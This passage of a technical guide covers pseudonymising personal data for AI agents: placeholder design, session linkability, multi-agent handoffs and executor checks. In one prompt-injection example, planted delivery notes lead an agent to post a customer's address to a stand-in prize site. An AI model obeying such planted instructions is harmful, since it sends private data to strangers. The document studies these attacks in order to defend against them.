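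Shortened names are even harder to restore. A chatbot may shorten Ashley Wise to Ashley, but software that replaced every "Ashley" would also change the name of Ashley County. SurrogateShield therefore searches for parts of a name only if the full name does not appear in the answer, so it can leave some shortened names unrestored.

An unrestored email address is more serious. If the executor fails to resolve EMAIL_1, the email system rejects it as an address, but it would accept an invented one, and Maria's confirmation could go to a stranger. The software can avoid this by inventing addresses that end in .invalid, which internet naming rules reserve so that no real address can use it.

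First names also suggest gender and origin. *One Persona, Many Cues, Different Results* (2026), a study of how language models adapt to users, uses them to give a model hints about a user. It takes names from North Carolina's voter register, choosing those where at least 90% of the people with the name share the same gender and ethnicity. If the software renamed Maria to John, the planner might call her "he" in a note to the courier, and restoring the name would not correct the pronoun. A woman's name would avoid that mistake but disclose her gender to the provider.

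The same conflict exists for language and region. SurrogateShield takes its surrogates from Faker, an open-source library of invented data. Jathanna notes that Faker favours Western names and US address formats. An American phone number in an order from Leeds might confuse the planner and would show an observer that the data is false.

*Locale-Conditioned Few-Shot Prompting Mitigates Demonstration Regurgitation in On-Device PII Substitution* (2026) describes a small local model that writes surrogates to fit the language and region of the text. The results read more naturally than Faker's in all six locales tested, according to a standard measure of text predictability. But they were less varied, and a name detector learned more from text with Faker's values. The study did not test agents, so it does not show whether a better regional match helps a planner.

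### Choosing a form for each value

One record can combine several forms. Deletion is best for values that no later step needs, such as Maria's date of birth when the agent is only moving a delivery. An opaque placeholder makes sense if the kind of value is itself sensitive, the surrounding text doesn't reveal what kind it is, and the planner only has to pass the value on.

A numbered typed placeholder is a sensible default for most names and contact details. Chen and colleagues' results suggest that it reduces accuracy only slightly, and the planner is unlikely to treat it as a real value. If a decision depends on part of the original value, such as a file extension that determines which program to use, the developer can keep that part.

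Surrogates are useful when a model or tool won't accept placeholders. Examples are SlotGuard's false keys and Attic Security's switch to surrogate email addresses after Claude ignored its tags. Surrogates also suit drafts in which the model needs a natural sentence and a person will check the restored text. For the "to" field of Maria's confirmation, the placeholder EMAIL_1 is safer.

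## How long a placeholder keeps its meaning

In Maria Keller's delivery, EMAIL_1 stands for the same address from her first message to the confirmation. If her message contained EMAIL_1 and the order record contained EMAIL_2, the planner could not tell whether the customer asking for Thursday had bought the cello, and it might refuse to move the delivery.

Over a year, the same consistency reduces her privacy. Suppose the shop always replaces her address with EMAIL_K7Q2. In March the provider learns that EMAIL_K7Q2 teaches on Tuesdays and lives near the Leeds South depot. In June she orders a quarter-size cello for her daughter, and in September she postpones a repair because of an operation. Perhaps none of these conversations identifies her, but the provider can link all three through the placeholder. If a fourth identifies her, the provider learns that the other three were hers too. Linkability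 is an observer's ability to tell that two placeholders or sessions concern the same person.

The shop uses one account with the model provider for all its customers, so a lasting placeholder may be the easiest way for the provider to pick out Maria's conversations. A personal assistant usually runs under its user's own account, so the provider can already link the sessions. In that case, lasting placeholders mainly expose the people the user writes about, such as a doctor or a sister.

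### Four lifetimes

| The placeholder stays the same for | What the planner can follow | What the provider can link through it |
|---|---|---|
| One message | A person within that message | Nothing beyond the message |
| One session | Maria through one task | The messages of that task |
| One user | Maria from one order to the next | All of Maria's sessions |
| Everyone, permanently | The same person in any customer's conversation | Every mention of that person by anyone |

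The last two rows differ for people like Mrs Okafor, the neighbour in Maria's delivery notes. If she is also a customer, a permanent placeholder links her own orders to Maria's notes, whereas per-user placeholders do not, because she has one in Maria's sessions and a different one in her own.

Placeholders that change with every message are nearly useless to an agent that has to act on the hidden data. In *PrivacyGuard*, Yuan and Li (2026) tested them on phone tasks that required a hidden phone number or address. Of the two planners tested, one completed none of its 30 runs and the other completed one.

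The usual compromise is to keep placeholders for one session, which requires a rule for when the session ends. PrivacyGuard ties a session to one continuing goal and, in its experiments, dropped the placeholder table after an hour without activity. If Maria asked on Friday where her cello was, she would start a new session and get new placeholders. Pookie's per-user namespaces control whose table may resolve a placeholder, not how long it lasts.

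### Counters, random tokens and keyed hashes

A counter is the simplest way to create placeholders. The executor gives each new value the next free number and stores the pair in the mapping table. If the count restarts with each session, EMAIL_1 stands for Maria's address today and someone else's tomorrow, so the provider learns nothing by comparing the two placeholders. But if an EMAIL_1 from Tuesday survives in a saved draft, the executor may use Friday's table to replace it with another customer's address. A counter that never restarts avoids this but reveals roughly how long ago each customer first appeared.

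With random tokens, the executor generates a random string such as EMAIL_x8f2k when it first meets a value. A token left over from an earlier table will almost certainly be missing from a later one, so the executor can stop instead of writing to a stranger. However, two machines that handle the same session have to share the table, or they will generate different tokens for the same address.

A keyed hash removes that need. Xia and Park compute the identifiers in SlotGuard as

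HMAC_*k*(type ‖ value)

where ‖ joins two strings and *k* is a secret key that is new for each session. Every machine that holds *k* gets the same result for Maria's address, although restoring the address still takes a table. The next session's key gives an unrelated result. Including the type keeps the surname Lincoln apart from the city of Lincoln. It also means that a detector that labels the same word as a name in one message and as a city in the next will produce two placeholders for it.

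The key is essential. If the shop used a public hash function such as SHA-256 without one, the provider could guess values the way a thief with Pookie's key could. There are ten billion ten-digit phone numbers, and at a billion hashes per second the provider needs

10¹⁰ ÷ 10⁹ = 10 seconds

to hash them all and find the one that matches. With a random 128-bit key, the provider would also have to guess the key, which is out of reach.

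*Anonymization-Enhanced Privacy Protection for Mobile GUI Agents* (Zhao, Zou and colleagues, 2026) describes "Available but Invisible", a system that protects people whose agents operate a phone. A placeholder such as PHONE_NUMBER#cbnhu consists of the type and the first five characters of a SHA-256 hash of the value and its type, written in digits and letters. Because the published formula has no key, it gives a phone number the same placeholder in every session and on every user's phone, even though the mapping table lasts for only one session.

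Cutting the hash to five characters gives some protection, because there are only about 60 million such codes and roughly 165 of the ten billion numbers share each one. But if a provider has a list of a million real phone numbers, each code will match an average of only about 0.02 of them by chance, so a hidden number that is on the list will usually be the only match.

### A new key for every session

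In *Veil-Then-Reveal*, Elmahallawy, Shaaban and Carroll (2026) describe software that runs on the user's device and replaces personal data with surrogates. Unlinkable sessions are an explicit goal. They assume the provider keeps everything and compares sessions, and they want to prevent it from directly matching the surrogates for one person.

The device holds a master key. For each session, a standard key-derivation function called HKDF combines the master key with the session's identifier:

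session key = HKDF(master key, session identifier)

The software uses the session key to derive one key for numbers and dates and another for names, places, organisations and email addresses. The results look random, so someone who learned Tuesday's session key could not calculate Friday's.

To replace a name, the software computes an HMAC of it and uses the result to pick an invented name from a long list. Maria Keller might become Helen Marsh throughout Tuesday's session and Joan Pryce throughout Friday's. If another person in the session already has the chosen name, the software changes a counter in the input and picks again. A table on the device records that Helen Marsh stands for Maria Keller. Phone and card numbers need no table because the software uses format-preserving encryption for them.

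When the session ends, the device discards the keys and the table. Nobody can then restore an old transcript, including Maria.

The main evaluation measures how much personal data reaches the provider and how well the software restores it, but not whether anyone can link two sessions. On 664 requests from PUPA, a collection of real chatbot conversations, 27.0% of the private values still reached the provider, compared with 95.1% without protection. Elmahallawy and colleagues attribute the remaining exposure mainly to values that the detector missed. These values look the same in every session, whatever the key, so someone could still use them to link sessions.

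Dates can link sessions in a subtler way. In one example, an article was written on 12 August 2014 and updated on 6 January 2017, 878 days later. Encrypting each date separately turned them into dates in 1981 and 1909, so the update appeared to come decades before the article. The software can instead shift all dates in a document by the same secret number of days, which keeps their order and the gaps between them. The secret number changes with each session but the 878-day gap stays the same, so a provider that saw this unusual gap in two sessions would have reason to connect them.

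The evaluation leaves out tool calls and long-term conversations, where an agent needs its placeholders most.

### What a new key cannot hide

Fresh keys prevent direct matching of placeholders, but Xia and Park acknowledge that the surrounding text and the visible ends of file paths can still link sessions. Whichever key is used, Maria's messages mention a cello and Tuesday lessons, and they keep her spelling, her greetings and her habit of explaining why she needs something.

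In *Can Prompt Anonymity Protect Your Identity From LLM Providers?*, Pham, Sheils and colleagues (2026) measured how much such traces reveal, using real conversations from WildChat (chatbot logs) and SWE-Chat (coding-agent sessions). Detected personal data had already been removed from both, and the researchers also removed file paths, web addresses, usernames and repository names from the coding sessions.

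The researchers treated the latest quarter of each collection as anonymous and the earlier conversations as the provider's records of known users. A language model turned each conversation into an embedding, a list of numbers that represents its content and style. The simplest attack assigned each anonymous conversation to the author of the most similar known one, or to nobody if the similarity was too low.

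With recent records, the attacks correctly linked at least one conversation for about 50% to 75% of the coding users and up to 10% of the chat users. Random guessing did so for no more than 5% of the coding users and 1% of the chat users. The threshold was set so that the attacks wrongly matched at most 10% of the people who were not in the records. The attacks were less successful with older records.

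One defence replaced identifiers with stable placeholders such as [PERSON_1] and removed signatures, emoji, unusual capitals and catchphrases, but it hardly changed the result. Pham and colleagues think this is partly because a user counts as identified if even one of their conversations is linked, so a defence has to work on all of them.

The provider can build a profile without a list of known users. In another test, the researchers grouped anonymous conversations by author without such a list. They scored the grouping from 0 to 1, with high scores when each group contained all of one author's conversations and nobody else's. The grouping scored about 0.45 to 0.6 on the coding sessions and 0.4 to 0.5 on the chats, while simple baselines scored 0.1 to 0.3.

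The coding result comes from only about 30 known users, and people who return to the same software project are easy to recognise by topic. A customer who writes to a cello shop twice a year leaves much less to compare. But even with placeholders, several sessions together can identify a person. *From Weak Cues to Real Identities* (2026) gives an example in which an agent combined masked chats with public information from the web.

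Changing the key is still worthwhile because it takes almost no effort and removes the only error-free way to link a person's sessions. If the key stayed the same, a provider could search its logs for EMAIL_K7Q2 and find all of Maria's sessions and nobody else's. Without that string, it has to compare the sessions' text and will sometimes match them wrongly.

### When the same address looks different

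Even within one session, software can fail to recognise a person's details when their format changes. Maria's order record contains "14 Linden Street, Leeds", but a courier's page might shorten the street to "14 Linden St" and show "Leeds" in a separate box. An executor that looks for exact matches treats these as new values.

In an example from Zhao and colleagues, an agent has to find a contact called Alice but cannot, because her name appears as FIRST_NAME#8dfa9 in the instruction and FIRST_NAME#g7wef on the screen. Their system therefore checks the session's mapping table before it creates a placeholder. It also keeps a list of words in the user's instruction that the detector did not mark as private. Those words stay readable for the whole session, even if the detector later marks one of them, because the provider has already seen them.

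For text recognised in screenshots, the system tolerates small differences. It counts the single-character changes that turn one string into the other and calculates

similarity = 1 − changes ÷ length of the longer string

The software reuses the old placeholder if the similarity is above 0.85. "14 Linden Street" has 16 characters, so one misread letter gives a similarity of 0.94 and the software correctly finds a match. "14 Linden St" lacks four characters, so its similarity is 0.75 and the software creates a new placeholder. The rule can also merge different people's data. "16 Linden Street" differs from Maria's address by one character, so if the neighbours' address appears on a later screen, the software would give it Maria's placeholder. Two eleven-digit phone numbers that differ in one digit score 0.91 and would also merge.

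Consistent placeholders worked better than a single fixed label in the team's tests on AndroidLab, a benchmark of 138 phone tasks. With screenshots as input, Gemini 3 Flash completed 70.3% of the tasks without protection, 63.8% with "Available but Invisible" and 55.8% when one fixed label replaced every private value. GPT-4o completed 44.2%, 40.6% and 34.8%, respectively.

PrivacyGuard stores a structured record for each person or thing instead of a list of strings. An address record has separate fields for the country, province, city, district, road and details such as the flat number. When another piece of an address appears, the software parses it and looks for a compatible record in the session. A record is compatible if it is of the same type, shares some identifying part with the new piece and does not contradict it. A missing field counts as unknown, so "14 Linden St", which has no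 town, can still match Maria's record. If several records are compatible, the software picks the most recently used. If none is, it creates a new record.

Neighbouring fragments on a screen can also belong to one record. In Yuan and Li's example, "5th Ave." and "Apt. 24B" appear in different places but are parts of the same New York address.

The records let the planner refer to part of a value. If Maria's address is `[[ADDR#1]]` and the courier's form has a box for the town, the planner can type `[[ADDR#1.CITY]]`. The software on the phone fills in "Leeds", which the planner never receives. The planner can refer to any part that the record contains, even one that no earlier placeholder mentioned. If the part is missing, the software leaves the placeholder as it is rather than filling in the full address.

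#### What the records achieved

Yuan and Li tested continuity on 7,800 versions of 240 addresses, with abbreviations, changed order, recognition errors and missing parts. They counted two versions of an address as consistent only if the software found both and gave them the same placeholder. With English addresses, PrivacyGuard scored 0.81, a variant of PrivacyGuard that reused placeholders only for exact matches scored 0.04, and "Available but Invisible" scored 0.15. With Chinese addresses, the scores were 0.82, 0.05 and 0, respectively. The researchers varied the addresses on purpose, so these scores don't show how often exact matching fails in ordinary use.

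They then gave two planners, a Qwen model and a Gemini model, tasks in the messaging app WeChat on an Android phone. Each had to find a phone number, a full address or part of an address in one chat and use it elsewhere. A run counted as a success only if the planner submitted a valid placeholder and the software restored the right value, so a correct guess in plain text did not count.

| How long the placeholder lasted | Qwen | Gemini |
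|---|---|---|
| One turn | 0 of 30 | 1 of 30 |
| The session, for exact matches only | 8 of 30 | 7 of 30 |
| The session, with structured records | 17 of 30 | 20 of 30 |

Of the 22 additional completions, 18 came from requests for part of a value, and 4 came from requests for a whole value, which both versions could make. In 18 of each planner's 30 runs, the task called for a city, a district or a flat number, which the exact-match version could not request. It failed all of these runs, while PrivacyGuard completed 6 with Qwen and 12 with Gemini. In the 12 runs that needed a whole value, the records raised the number of completions from 8 to 11 with Qwen and from 7 to 8 with Gemini.

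On AndroidLab's more varied tasks, PrivacyGuard's completion rate was 0 to 5.8 percentage points higher than that of "Available but Invisible", depending on the planner. The difference was distinguishable from chance for only one of four planners.

PrivacyGuard also exposed fewer private values than "Available but Invisible". Yuan and Li had two models try to recover these values from everything a provider would receive in a five-turn session. In English, the models recovered 21% to 22% of the values with PrivacyGuard, compared with 33% to 35% with "Available but Invisible". In Chinese, they recovered 12% to 14%, compared with 70% to 72%. Nearly all of this exposure came from individual messages and screenshots, and combining the five turns added at most 0.3 percentage points.

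The models worked out the exact value behind 1.3% to 1.6% of PrivacyGuard's placeholders from a single screen or message, and about 3% from five turns. The two tests cover different sets of placeholders, but a higher rate is what one would expect when an observer can follow the same placeholder for longer.

#### Two people under one placeholder

A tolerant matching rule can also give one placeholder to two people. In 480 test sessions, PrivacyGuard reused an existing record 4,352 times, and it was the correct record every time. Yuan and Li also generated 6,000 cases in which a new fragment belonged to an earlier address. In some of these cases, the fragment fitted other addresses too.

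In 4,236 of these cases, only one record was compatible, and the software chose it. In the other 1,764, several were compatible. Picking the most recent was right 1,050 times and wrong 714 times, an error rate of about 40%. Creating a new record whenever there was doubt would have made no false merges but split one address in two all 1,764 times.

For Maria, a split is the safer mistake. The planner might have to ask which address she means, whereas a false merge could send her cello to 14 Linden Street in York. Beskorovainyi's engine is cautious in the same way and gives an ambiguous surname its own placeholder. PrivacyGuard's rule suits tasks in which a person sees the result before anything irreversible happens.

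### Memory that outlasts the session

Many agents keep notes between sessions. After the delivery, the shop's agent might write "NAME_1 prefers Thursdays, because she teaches on Tuesdays". Once the session's table is gone, nobody can tell whom the note is about. If the next session also numbers its placeholders from 1, the agent may apply the note to a different customer.

The obvious remedy is to keep the table as long as the notes. In the MemPrivacy tests, typed placeholders worked almost as well as real values in an agent's memory, but only because the software could still restore them. If the planner sees the same placeholders in every session, though, the provider can build the profile described at the start of this section.

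The shop can avoid this by separating the lasting identity from the placeholder. It would give Maria an internal record number, say 8812, that never leaves its own machines, and store the note under that number. When she returns, the executor loads the note and writes that session's placeholder into it:

| Where | March | June |
|---|---|---|
| Shop's own memory | Customer 8812 prefers Thursdays | Customer 8812 prefers Thursdays |
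| What the planner reads | NAME_h4t prefers Thursdays | NAME_w9c prefers Thursdays |

The arrangement requires the shop to store and search the notes itself. If the model provider hosts the memory, the stored text needs placeholders that stay valid across sessions, and the provider can link them. Even with local storage, the planner reads the same sentence about Thursdays in both sessions, which can link the two. The agent can reduce this risk by loading only the notes the current task needs.

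PrivacyGuard makes a similar separation for a different purpose. Users can keep a permanent list of their own names, addresses and aliases on the phone to help the detector recognise them. Only the current session's table can restore values, so a planner cannot obtain a value merely because it is on the list.

A lasting table also creates a new risk, since it holds in one place everything the placeholders hide. The shop should delete entries it no longer needs, but how well deletion cuts the link to a customer depends on how the shop makes its placeholders. If it uses random tokens, deleting Maria's row leaves nothing to connect her to the old token in the provider's logs, and she gets a new token if she orders again. If it uses a keyed hash with a permanent key, deleting the row achieves much less, because her address will produce the same placeholder the next time it appears and reconnect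 her to the old logs. Anyone with the key can also test whether a placeholder in those logs is hers.

The shop therefore has to delete the key as well as the row. If all customers share one key, deleting it changes everyone's placeholders, so each customer should have a separate key. Data can also survive in copies. PrivacyGuard normally keeps its table only in memory, but an optional audit mode writes it to a file with the real values, and Yuan and Li do not promise that the file can be securely deleted. Deleting the shop's data also does not remove the provider's copy of the text around the placeholders.

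Deleting the table too early also causes problems. If the courier reports a failed delivery on Thursday and Tuesday's table has been deleted, an agent that kept only placeholders cannot identify the person to notify.

### Handing a placeholder to another agent

Larger agents split their work among subagents, each with its own planner. Suppose the shop's order agent runs on provider A's model and passes the rebooking to a delivery agent on provider B's model. The executor can use one mapping table for both or a separate one for each.

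| | Provider A reads | Provider B reads |
|---|---|---|
| One shared table | NAME_h4t teaches on Tuesdays and has bought a cello | NAME_h4t lives in the area of the Leeds South depot |
| Separate tables | NAME_h4t teaches on Tuesdays and has bought a cello | NAME_p2m lives in the area of the Leeds South depot |

A shared table makes the handoff simple because NAME_h4t refers to Maria for both agents. But if the providers compared their records, or a thief obtained both logs, a single search for the placeholder would link the two sessions. Random tokens and keyed hashes are easy to match this way because each is practically unique. A plain NAME_1 occurs in thousands of sessions, so an observer would also need the time or an order number to find the two that belong together.

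Separate tables remove that link but require translation at every handoff. The executor intercepts the order agent's message, resolves NAME_h4t to Maria Keller, looks her up in the delivery agent's table and writes NAME_p2m. It does the reverse for replies. If both tables used plain counters and the executor missed a placeholder, NAME_1 might refer to a different customer in the delivery agent's table. Random tokens are safer here too, because an untranslated one fails to resolve.

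Translation can also give one person two placeholders in the same table. Suppose the courier's page calls the recipient "M. Keller". The delivery agent's table has no such name, so the executor creates NAME_c7x and later looks for "M. Keller" in the order agent's table. It finds nothing there either and adds another placeholder. The order agent now sees what look like two customers and may report that the courier has the wrong recipient. A shared table has the same problem, but the software has to connect the two forms of the name only once, rather than in each agent's table.

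The internal record number from the previous section solves much of this. The shop keeps one private register of people and gives each agent its own key, which it can derive from the session key in the way Veil-Then-Reveal derives keys for different kinds of data. The placeholder is then

HMAC_*agent key*(type ‖ record number)

Both spellings of Maria's name lead to record 8812, so each agent has one placeholder for her. The two providers have different placeholders. However, a false merge in the register affects all agents at once.

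Separate placeholders protect little if the surrounding text matches. When the order agent writes "Please move order 58213 to Thursday", the sentence ends up in both providers' logs, and the order number links the two logs as effectively as a name would. The executor would have to replace the order number too, and the order agent should pass on only what the delivery agent needs. If both agents use the same provider, that provider receives the text from both, so separate tables achieve little.

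Agents tend to pass on far more data than necessary. *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) tested five models from 2024 on 1,000 scenarios in healthcare, finance, law and business. A typical scenario contained 29 private fields, and the task required three of them. The researchers counted a leak whenever a message or store contained at least one field that did not belong there.

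| Where the data appeared | Share of runs with a leak |
|---|---|
| Messages between agents | 68.8% |
| Memory shared by agents | 46.7% |
| Final answer, several agents | 27.2% |
| Final answer, single agent | 43.2% |

Dividing the work made the final answers cleaner but moved the leaks to places users don't see. This pattern held for all five models, but the percentages are a poor guide to current systems because half of the scenarios included an attack and newer models may behave differently.

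The agents in these measurements exchanged raw data, so the results cannot show how much placeholders would help. El Yagoubi and colleagues found only 18% of the leaks by searching for planted markers and values in a recognisable format, such as social security numbers. They found the rest with a language model, including paraphrased facts such as diagnoses. An executor that swaps names and numbers at each handoff would leave many of those facts in the message.

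No published study appears to compare a shared table with separate ones, either for which records providers could link or for how many tasks fail when placeholders are translated. Until one does, the shop's choice depends mainly on whether its agents use different providers. If they do, separate placeholders from one private register protect personal data better. If they all use the same provider, a shared table is simpler and gives up almost no protection.

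## What the executor checks before it restores a value

A planner can send Maria Keller's address to the wrong party without ever reading it, because naming the placeholder is enough. Suppose the shop's agent also has a tool called `post_form`, which files damage claims on the courier's website. Someone plants a sentence in the delivery notes that tells the agent to enter every customer in a prize draw, and the planner obeys:

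```
post_form(site="parcel-prizes.example", address="ADDRESS_1")
```

An executor that resolves every placeholder can post a user's address, such as 14 Linden Street, to a stranger's website. Computer scientists call such an executor a confused deputy, meaning a program that uses its own authority on behalf of someone who lacks that authority.

The same problem exists with API keys, the passwords that give software access to a service. Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, tested their own company's vault, which adds the key to a request so that the agent never reads it. They also used their own judgement to score several threats from 1 to 25, with and without the vault. With the vault, the score for pasting a secret into a prompt fell from 25 to 4, but the score for a key with too many permissions fell only from 20 to 15,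 because an agent that cannot read a key can still use it to delete something.

### Five checks in order

The executor first looks for the placeholder in the current session's mapping table. It then compares the placeholder's type in the table with the type the argument expects, which would catch NAME_1 in the `to` field of an email. This check does little for free-text arguments such as `body` or `notes`, which accept any type. Shayesteh and Wilson, whom *ArguShield* cites, found at least one such argument in 36.9% of 2,344 tool specifications for custom versions of ChatGPT.

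For the other three checks, the executor needs a policy that covers tools, recipients and human approval. The shop's policy might look like this:

| Type of value | Tool and argument | Permitted recipient | Ask a person? |
|---|---|---|---|
| EMAIL | `find_order`, email | Order database | No |
| ADDRESS | `move_delivery`, address | Courier | No |
| EMAIL | `send_email`, to | Customer named in the order | No |
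| NAME | `send_email`, body | Customer named in the order | No |
| ADDRESS | `post_form`, address | Courier's claims page | Yes |
| Anything else | Any | Nobody | – |

The last row makes this a default-deny policy, because the executor refuses whatever the shop has not listed. Two calls with the same placeholder then end differently:

| Check | `move_delivery` with ADDRESS_1 | `post_form` to parcel-prizes.example with ADDRESS_1 |
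|---|---|---|
| Does the placeholder exist in this session? | Yes | Yes |
| Does its type fit the argument? | Yes | Yes |
| May this tool receive it? | Yes | Yes, for damage claims |
| Is the recipient on the list? | Yes, the courier | No, so the executor refuses |
| Must a person approve? | No, so the executor restores the address | The call never gets this far |

The recipient check is easy for `move_delivery`, which always contacts the courier. In `post_form` and `send_email`, the planner writes the recipient into the call, so the executor has to resolve any placeholder in that argument before checking the recipient. If the delivery notes contain an attacker's email address, the planner might receive it only as EMAIL_2. The shop can require the recipient's address to come from the order record, but then the mapping table has to store where each value came from, much as CaMeL's labels do.

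A value entered on a web page may go to a different site from the one in the address bar, as when a shop's page embeds a payment company's form. *Sensitive data*, Browser Use's guide for developers of agents that operate a browser, describes a check on the frame that contains the form field. Browser Use lets developers list the hostnames where the agent may enter each secret, although the agent can still visit other sites.

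Kenney and colleagues' vault also ties each key to one host. In their tests, three websites that send back whatever they receive did not receive the key. All 16 probes gave the expected result, but none tested whether a redirect could carry a key from an approved host to another.

Human approval comes last because it takes the most effort. Kenney and colleagues recommend it for actions such as transfers, deletions, publication and bulk exports. *The OpenHands Software Agent SDK* (2025) describes a coding-agent toolkit that uses a risk rating for each tool call to decide whether approval is needed. In the built-in version, a language model supplies the rating. If the same model also plans the call, a planted instruction can distort both the call and its rating.

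The person also needs to see the real values, since an employee can answer "Send 14 Linden Street, Leeds to parcel-prizes.example?" but not "Send ADDRESS_1?" The executor itself has to write the question and show it outside the conversation, or the address will reach the planner.

### When a placeholder does not exist

Models fairly often write placeholders that no software has issued. In the last round of tests in *Reversible Pseudonymisation of Documents Sent to External LLMs*, one model did this 106 times in 760 answers and the other never did. On an earlier set of documents, the same two models invented 89 and 47 placeholders.

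The restorer in *PromptGraph* leaves such placeholders unresolved. Its own placeholders are opaque, such as [P1], and it checks them against details kept in a private table, including the type of each hidden value. The tests measured how well the system hides data and how useful the answers remain, but not how often these checks prevent a mistake or block a valid placeholder.

An unresolved placeholder, which only looks odd in a chatbot's answer, can do harm in a tool call. For example, a courier's system might accept "ADDRESS_2" as a street name. An executor should therefore cancel the whole call and tell the planner why. Browser Use does this when an agent uses an outdated placeholder format. It enters nothing in the form and returns an error message that names the correct function. SlotGuard also rejects invalid placeholders.

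Beskorovainyi's engine repairs small changes to a placeholder, such as a missing bracket. This is fairly safe when the type and number still match only one entry and a person will read the result. For a tool call, asking the planner to write the placeholder again takes one more request but avoids guessing.

These five checks don't catch a real placeholder used in the wrong place. If Maria's record also contained a billing address, ADDRESS_2, and the planner used it instead of the delivery address, the call would pass every check and the cello would go to the wrong house. To catch the error, the executor would have to compare the call with the order or ask Maria.

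### A vault that refuses by default

Hidet's *mcp-pvp* is an open-source library that applies a default-deny policy to tools connected through the Model Context Protocol. Each rule specifies a type of value, a tool and an argument, such as an email address in the "to" field of `send_email`.

When the planner calls that tool with a placeholder, the vault checks the policy and creates a grant, a signed permission to restore this one value. According to Hidet's *Capability Security Design*, the grant is valid only for one session, one tool and one argument, and expires after five minutes by default. The vault verifies the grant, inserts the value and runs the tool. The developers estimate in an article on Ready Tensor that the real value is in memory for about 50 milliseconds.

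The first version issued a grant as soon as it replaced a value, and any tool could use that grant. A misled agent could therefore have used a grant meant for `send_email` with a tool that sends data to an attacker. The current version refuses such a call. It also refuses to use a grant for the "to" field in the "bcc" field, where the restored address could add a hidden recipient.

The grants add less protection than they seem to. In the mode that Hidet's *Privacy Vault Protocol (PVP) v1* recommends, the vault issues a grant for any call the planner has written, provided the policy permits it. Whether a grant is issued therefore depends on the policy, and the grant mainly stops other software from reusing the permission. Hidet intends each grant for a single use but lists enforced one-time grants only as a possible future addition, so a stolen grant might work repeatedly until it expires.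 The sample policy allows email addresses in "to", "cc" and "bcc", so it does not distinguish between these fields.

The rules also don't specify a recipient, so if the shop allowed addresses in the body of `send_email`, the vault would restore Maria's address in an email to anyone. The shop could instead offer a narrower tool, say `email_customer`, that always sends to the email address in the order record. A cap on releases per step, 50 in one sample policy, limits how much personal data the planner can extract at once.

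Hidet's documents are inconsistent on whether an operator can permit release to a language model. The Ready Tensor article rules it out, while the protocol allows it if someone explicitly enables it. Hidet's *Threat Model* warns that the vault will carry out a policy even if it is too permissive.

### Calls that release more than the task needs

A call can satisfy the shop's policy and still contain more personal data than the task needs. The courier may receive Maria's address to move her delivery, but it doesn't need her billing address as well. *ArguShield* describes software that examines every value in a proposed call and decides whether to keep it, hide it or ask the user.

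The executor checks where the value came from, whether the task needs it and whether this tool is a suitable recipient, then applies fixed rules to decide what to do. It can send a value immediately if the user has just supplied it for the task and the tool needs it. If a useful value comes from a stored profile, the executor asks the user first. It hides values that the model seems to have made up and those that the recipient should not have.

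The researchers tested four models on 120 synthetic tasks in travel, shopping and healthcare. Half were "high-risk" tasks, with stricter limits on who may receive what. In the averages below, a value counts as released if the software sent it without asking when it should have asked or hidden the value.

| Protection | Released, standard tasks | Completed, standard tasks | Released, high-risk tasks | Completed, high-risk tasks |
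|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 84% | 97% | 76% | 97% |
| Privacy instruction in the prompt | 4% | 75% | 4% | 69% |
| ArguShield | 9% | 97% | 6% | 97% |

The instruction resulted in the least leakage but made the models withhold values the tools needed. ArguShield's completion rates assume the user approves every request. If the user rejected every request, 93% of tasks would still succeed.

The software asked for approval of roughly a fifth of all values in completed tasks. Approving only the first one in each call would have completed just as many tasks with about 41% fewer approvals. No real users took part, so the tests don't show whether people would read that many requests.

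The leaks that remained were mostly minor. Of the data it should have held back, ArguShield released only 1% to 2% of medical, financial and similar data, but 42% to 55% of low-consequence details such as preferences and schedules. Maria's remark about teaching on Tuesdays is one such detail.

The approach also reduced leaks with tools the researchers had not designed. With tool definitions from 26 real servers, the share of tasks with a leak fell from 92% to 4%. On 123 tasks from AgentDAM, a benchmark for web agents, the share fell from 80% to 20%, while task completion dropped from 97% to 94%.

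These results may be optimistic, because ArguShield uses each task's success criteria to determine what the task needs, and a shop rarely has such criteria in writing. Placeholders would make it easier to find where a value came from. ArguShield has to match each value against the user's profile and earlier tool results, whereas a mapping table can store the source from the start.

### How restored values come back

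After the executor restores a value, the tool's response may contain it. `send_email` might return a confirmation that includes the address maria.keller@example.org, or the courier's system might reject a booking with the error "No postcode found for 14 Linden Street, Leeds". If the executor passes the response on unchanged, the planner and its provider receive the value after all.

The executor can search for the values it has just restored, which gives it an advantage over a detector that reads unfamiliar text. *The OpenHands Software Agent SDK* describes such a search for passwords and keys, which replaces every secret with the same mask. Using one mask for personal data would hide from the planner whether the confirmation went to Maria or to someone else.

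mcp-pvp instead runs its detector over each result, including error messages, and creates new placeholders for what it finds. The planner would then see a second placeholder for Maria's email address and might take it for another customer's. The default detector also doesn't look for names or street addresses, so the courier's error message would pass through unchanged unless the shop installed the Presidio option.

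A tool can also return a value in a different form. Browser Use searches for each secret in upper and lower case, backwards and in several common encodings. This search would still miss an abbreviated address such as "14 LINDEN ST", or a value that a misled planner had told a tool to return with hyphens between the letters. The executor should therefore be especially restrictive about restoring values for general-purpose tools, such as one that runs code. Browser Use warns that code written by the model can read the secrets directly from the process that holds them.

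Text searches don't catch personal data in screenshots. Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely* warns that anything visible in a tab where Claude is working becomes part of the conversation. If the executor types Maria's address into a web form, the next screenshot may show it to the planner.

Browser Use does not redact screenshots, and an older version of its instructions (Browser Use) advises developers to turn off the model's vision. That works only if the agent can operate the page from its text. The executor could also cover the field it has just filled, but many sites repeat a value such as an address on the next page, and the executor would need a screenshot detector to find it there.

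### The most valuable target

The executor holds the mapping table, the policy and often the credentials for the tools. Anyone who breaks into it can read the customers' data without misleading the planner.

Attacks on the LiteLLM gateway show that such software is an attractive target. In April 2026, attackers began exploiting a flaw in its database queries about 36 hours after the public warning. Security Affairs' *CVE-2026-42208* reports that they went straight for the three tables with the most valuable secrets, including the stored credentials for model providers. SC Media's *LiteLLM exploited within 36 hours of disclosure via SQL injection bug* quotes an expert who points out that the gateway also holds prompts and responses. If the gateway restored placeholders as well, it would also hold what is needed to read the redacted prompts and responses.

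The flaw could also let an attacker change the mapping table, which may be worse than reading it. An attacker who replaced the address behind EMAIL_1 with their own would receive Maria's confirmation, and the call could still pass every check. The executor can guard against this by comparing the restored address with the one in the order database, unless the attacker has access to that database too.

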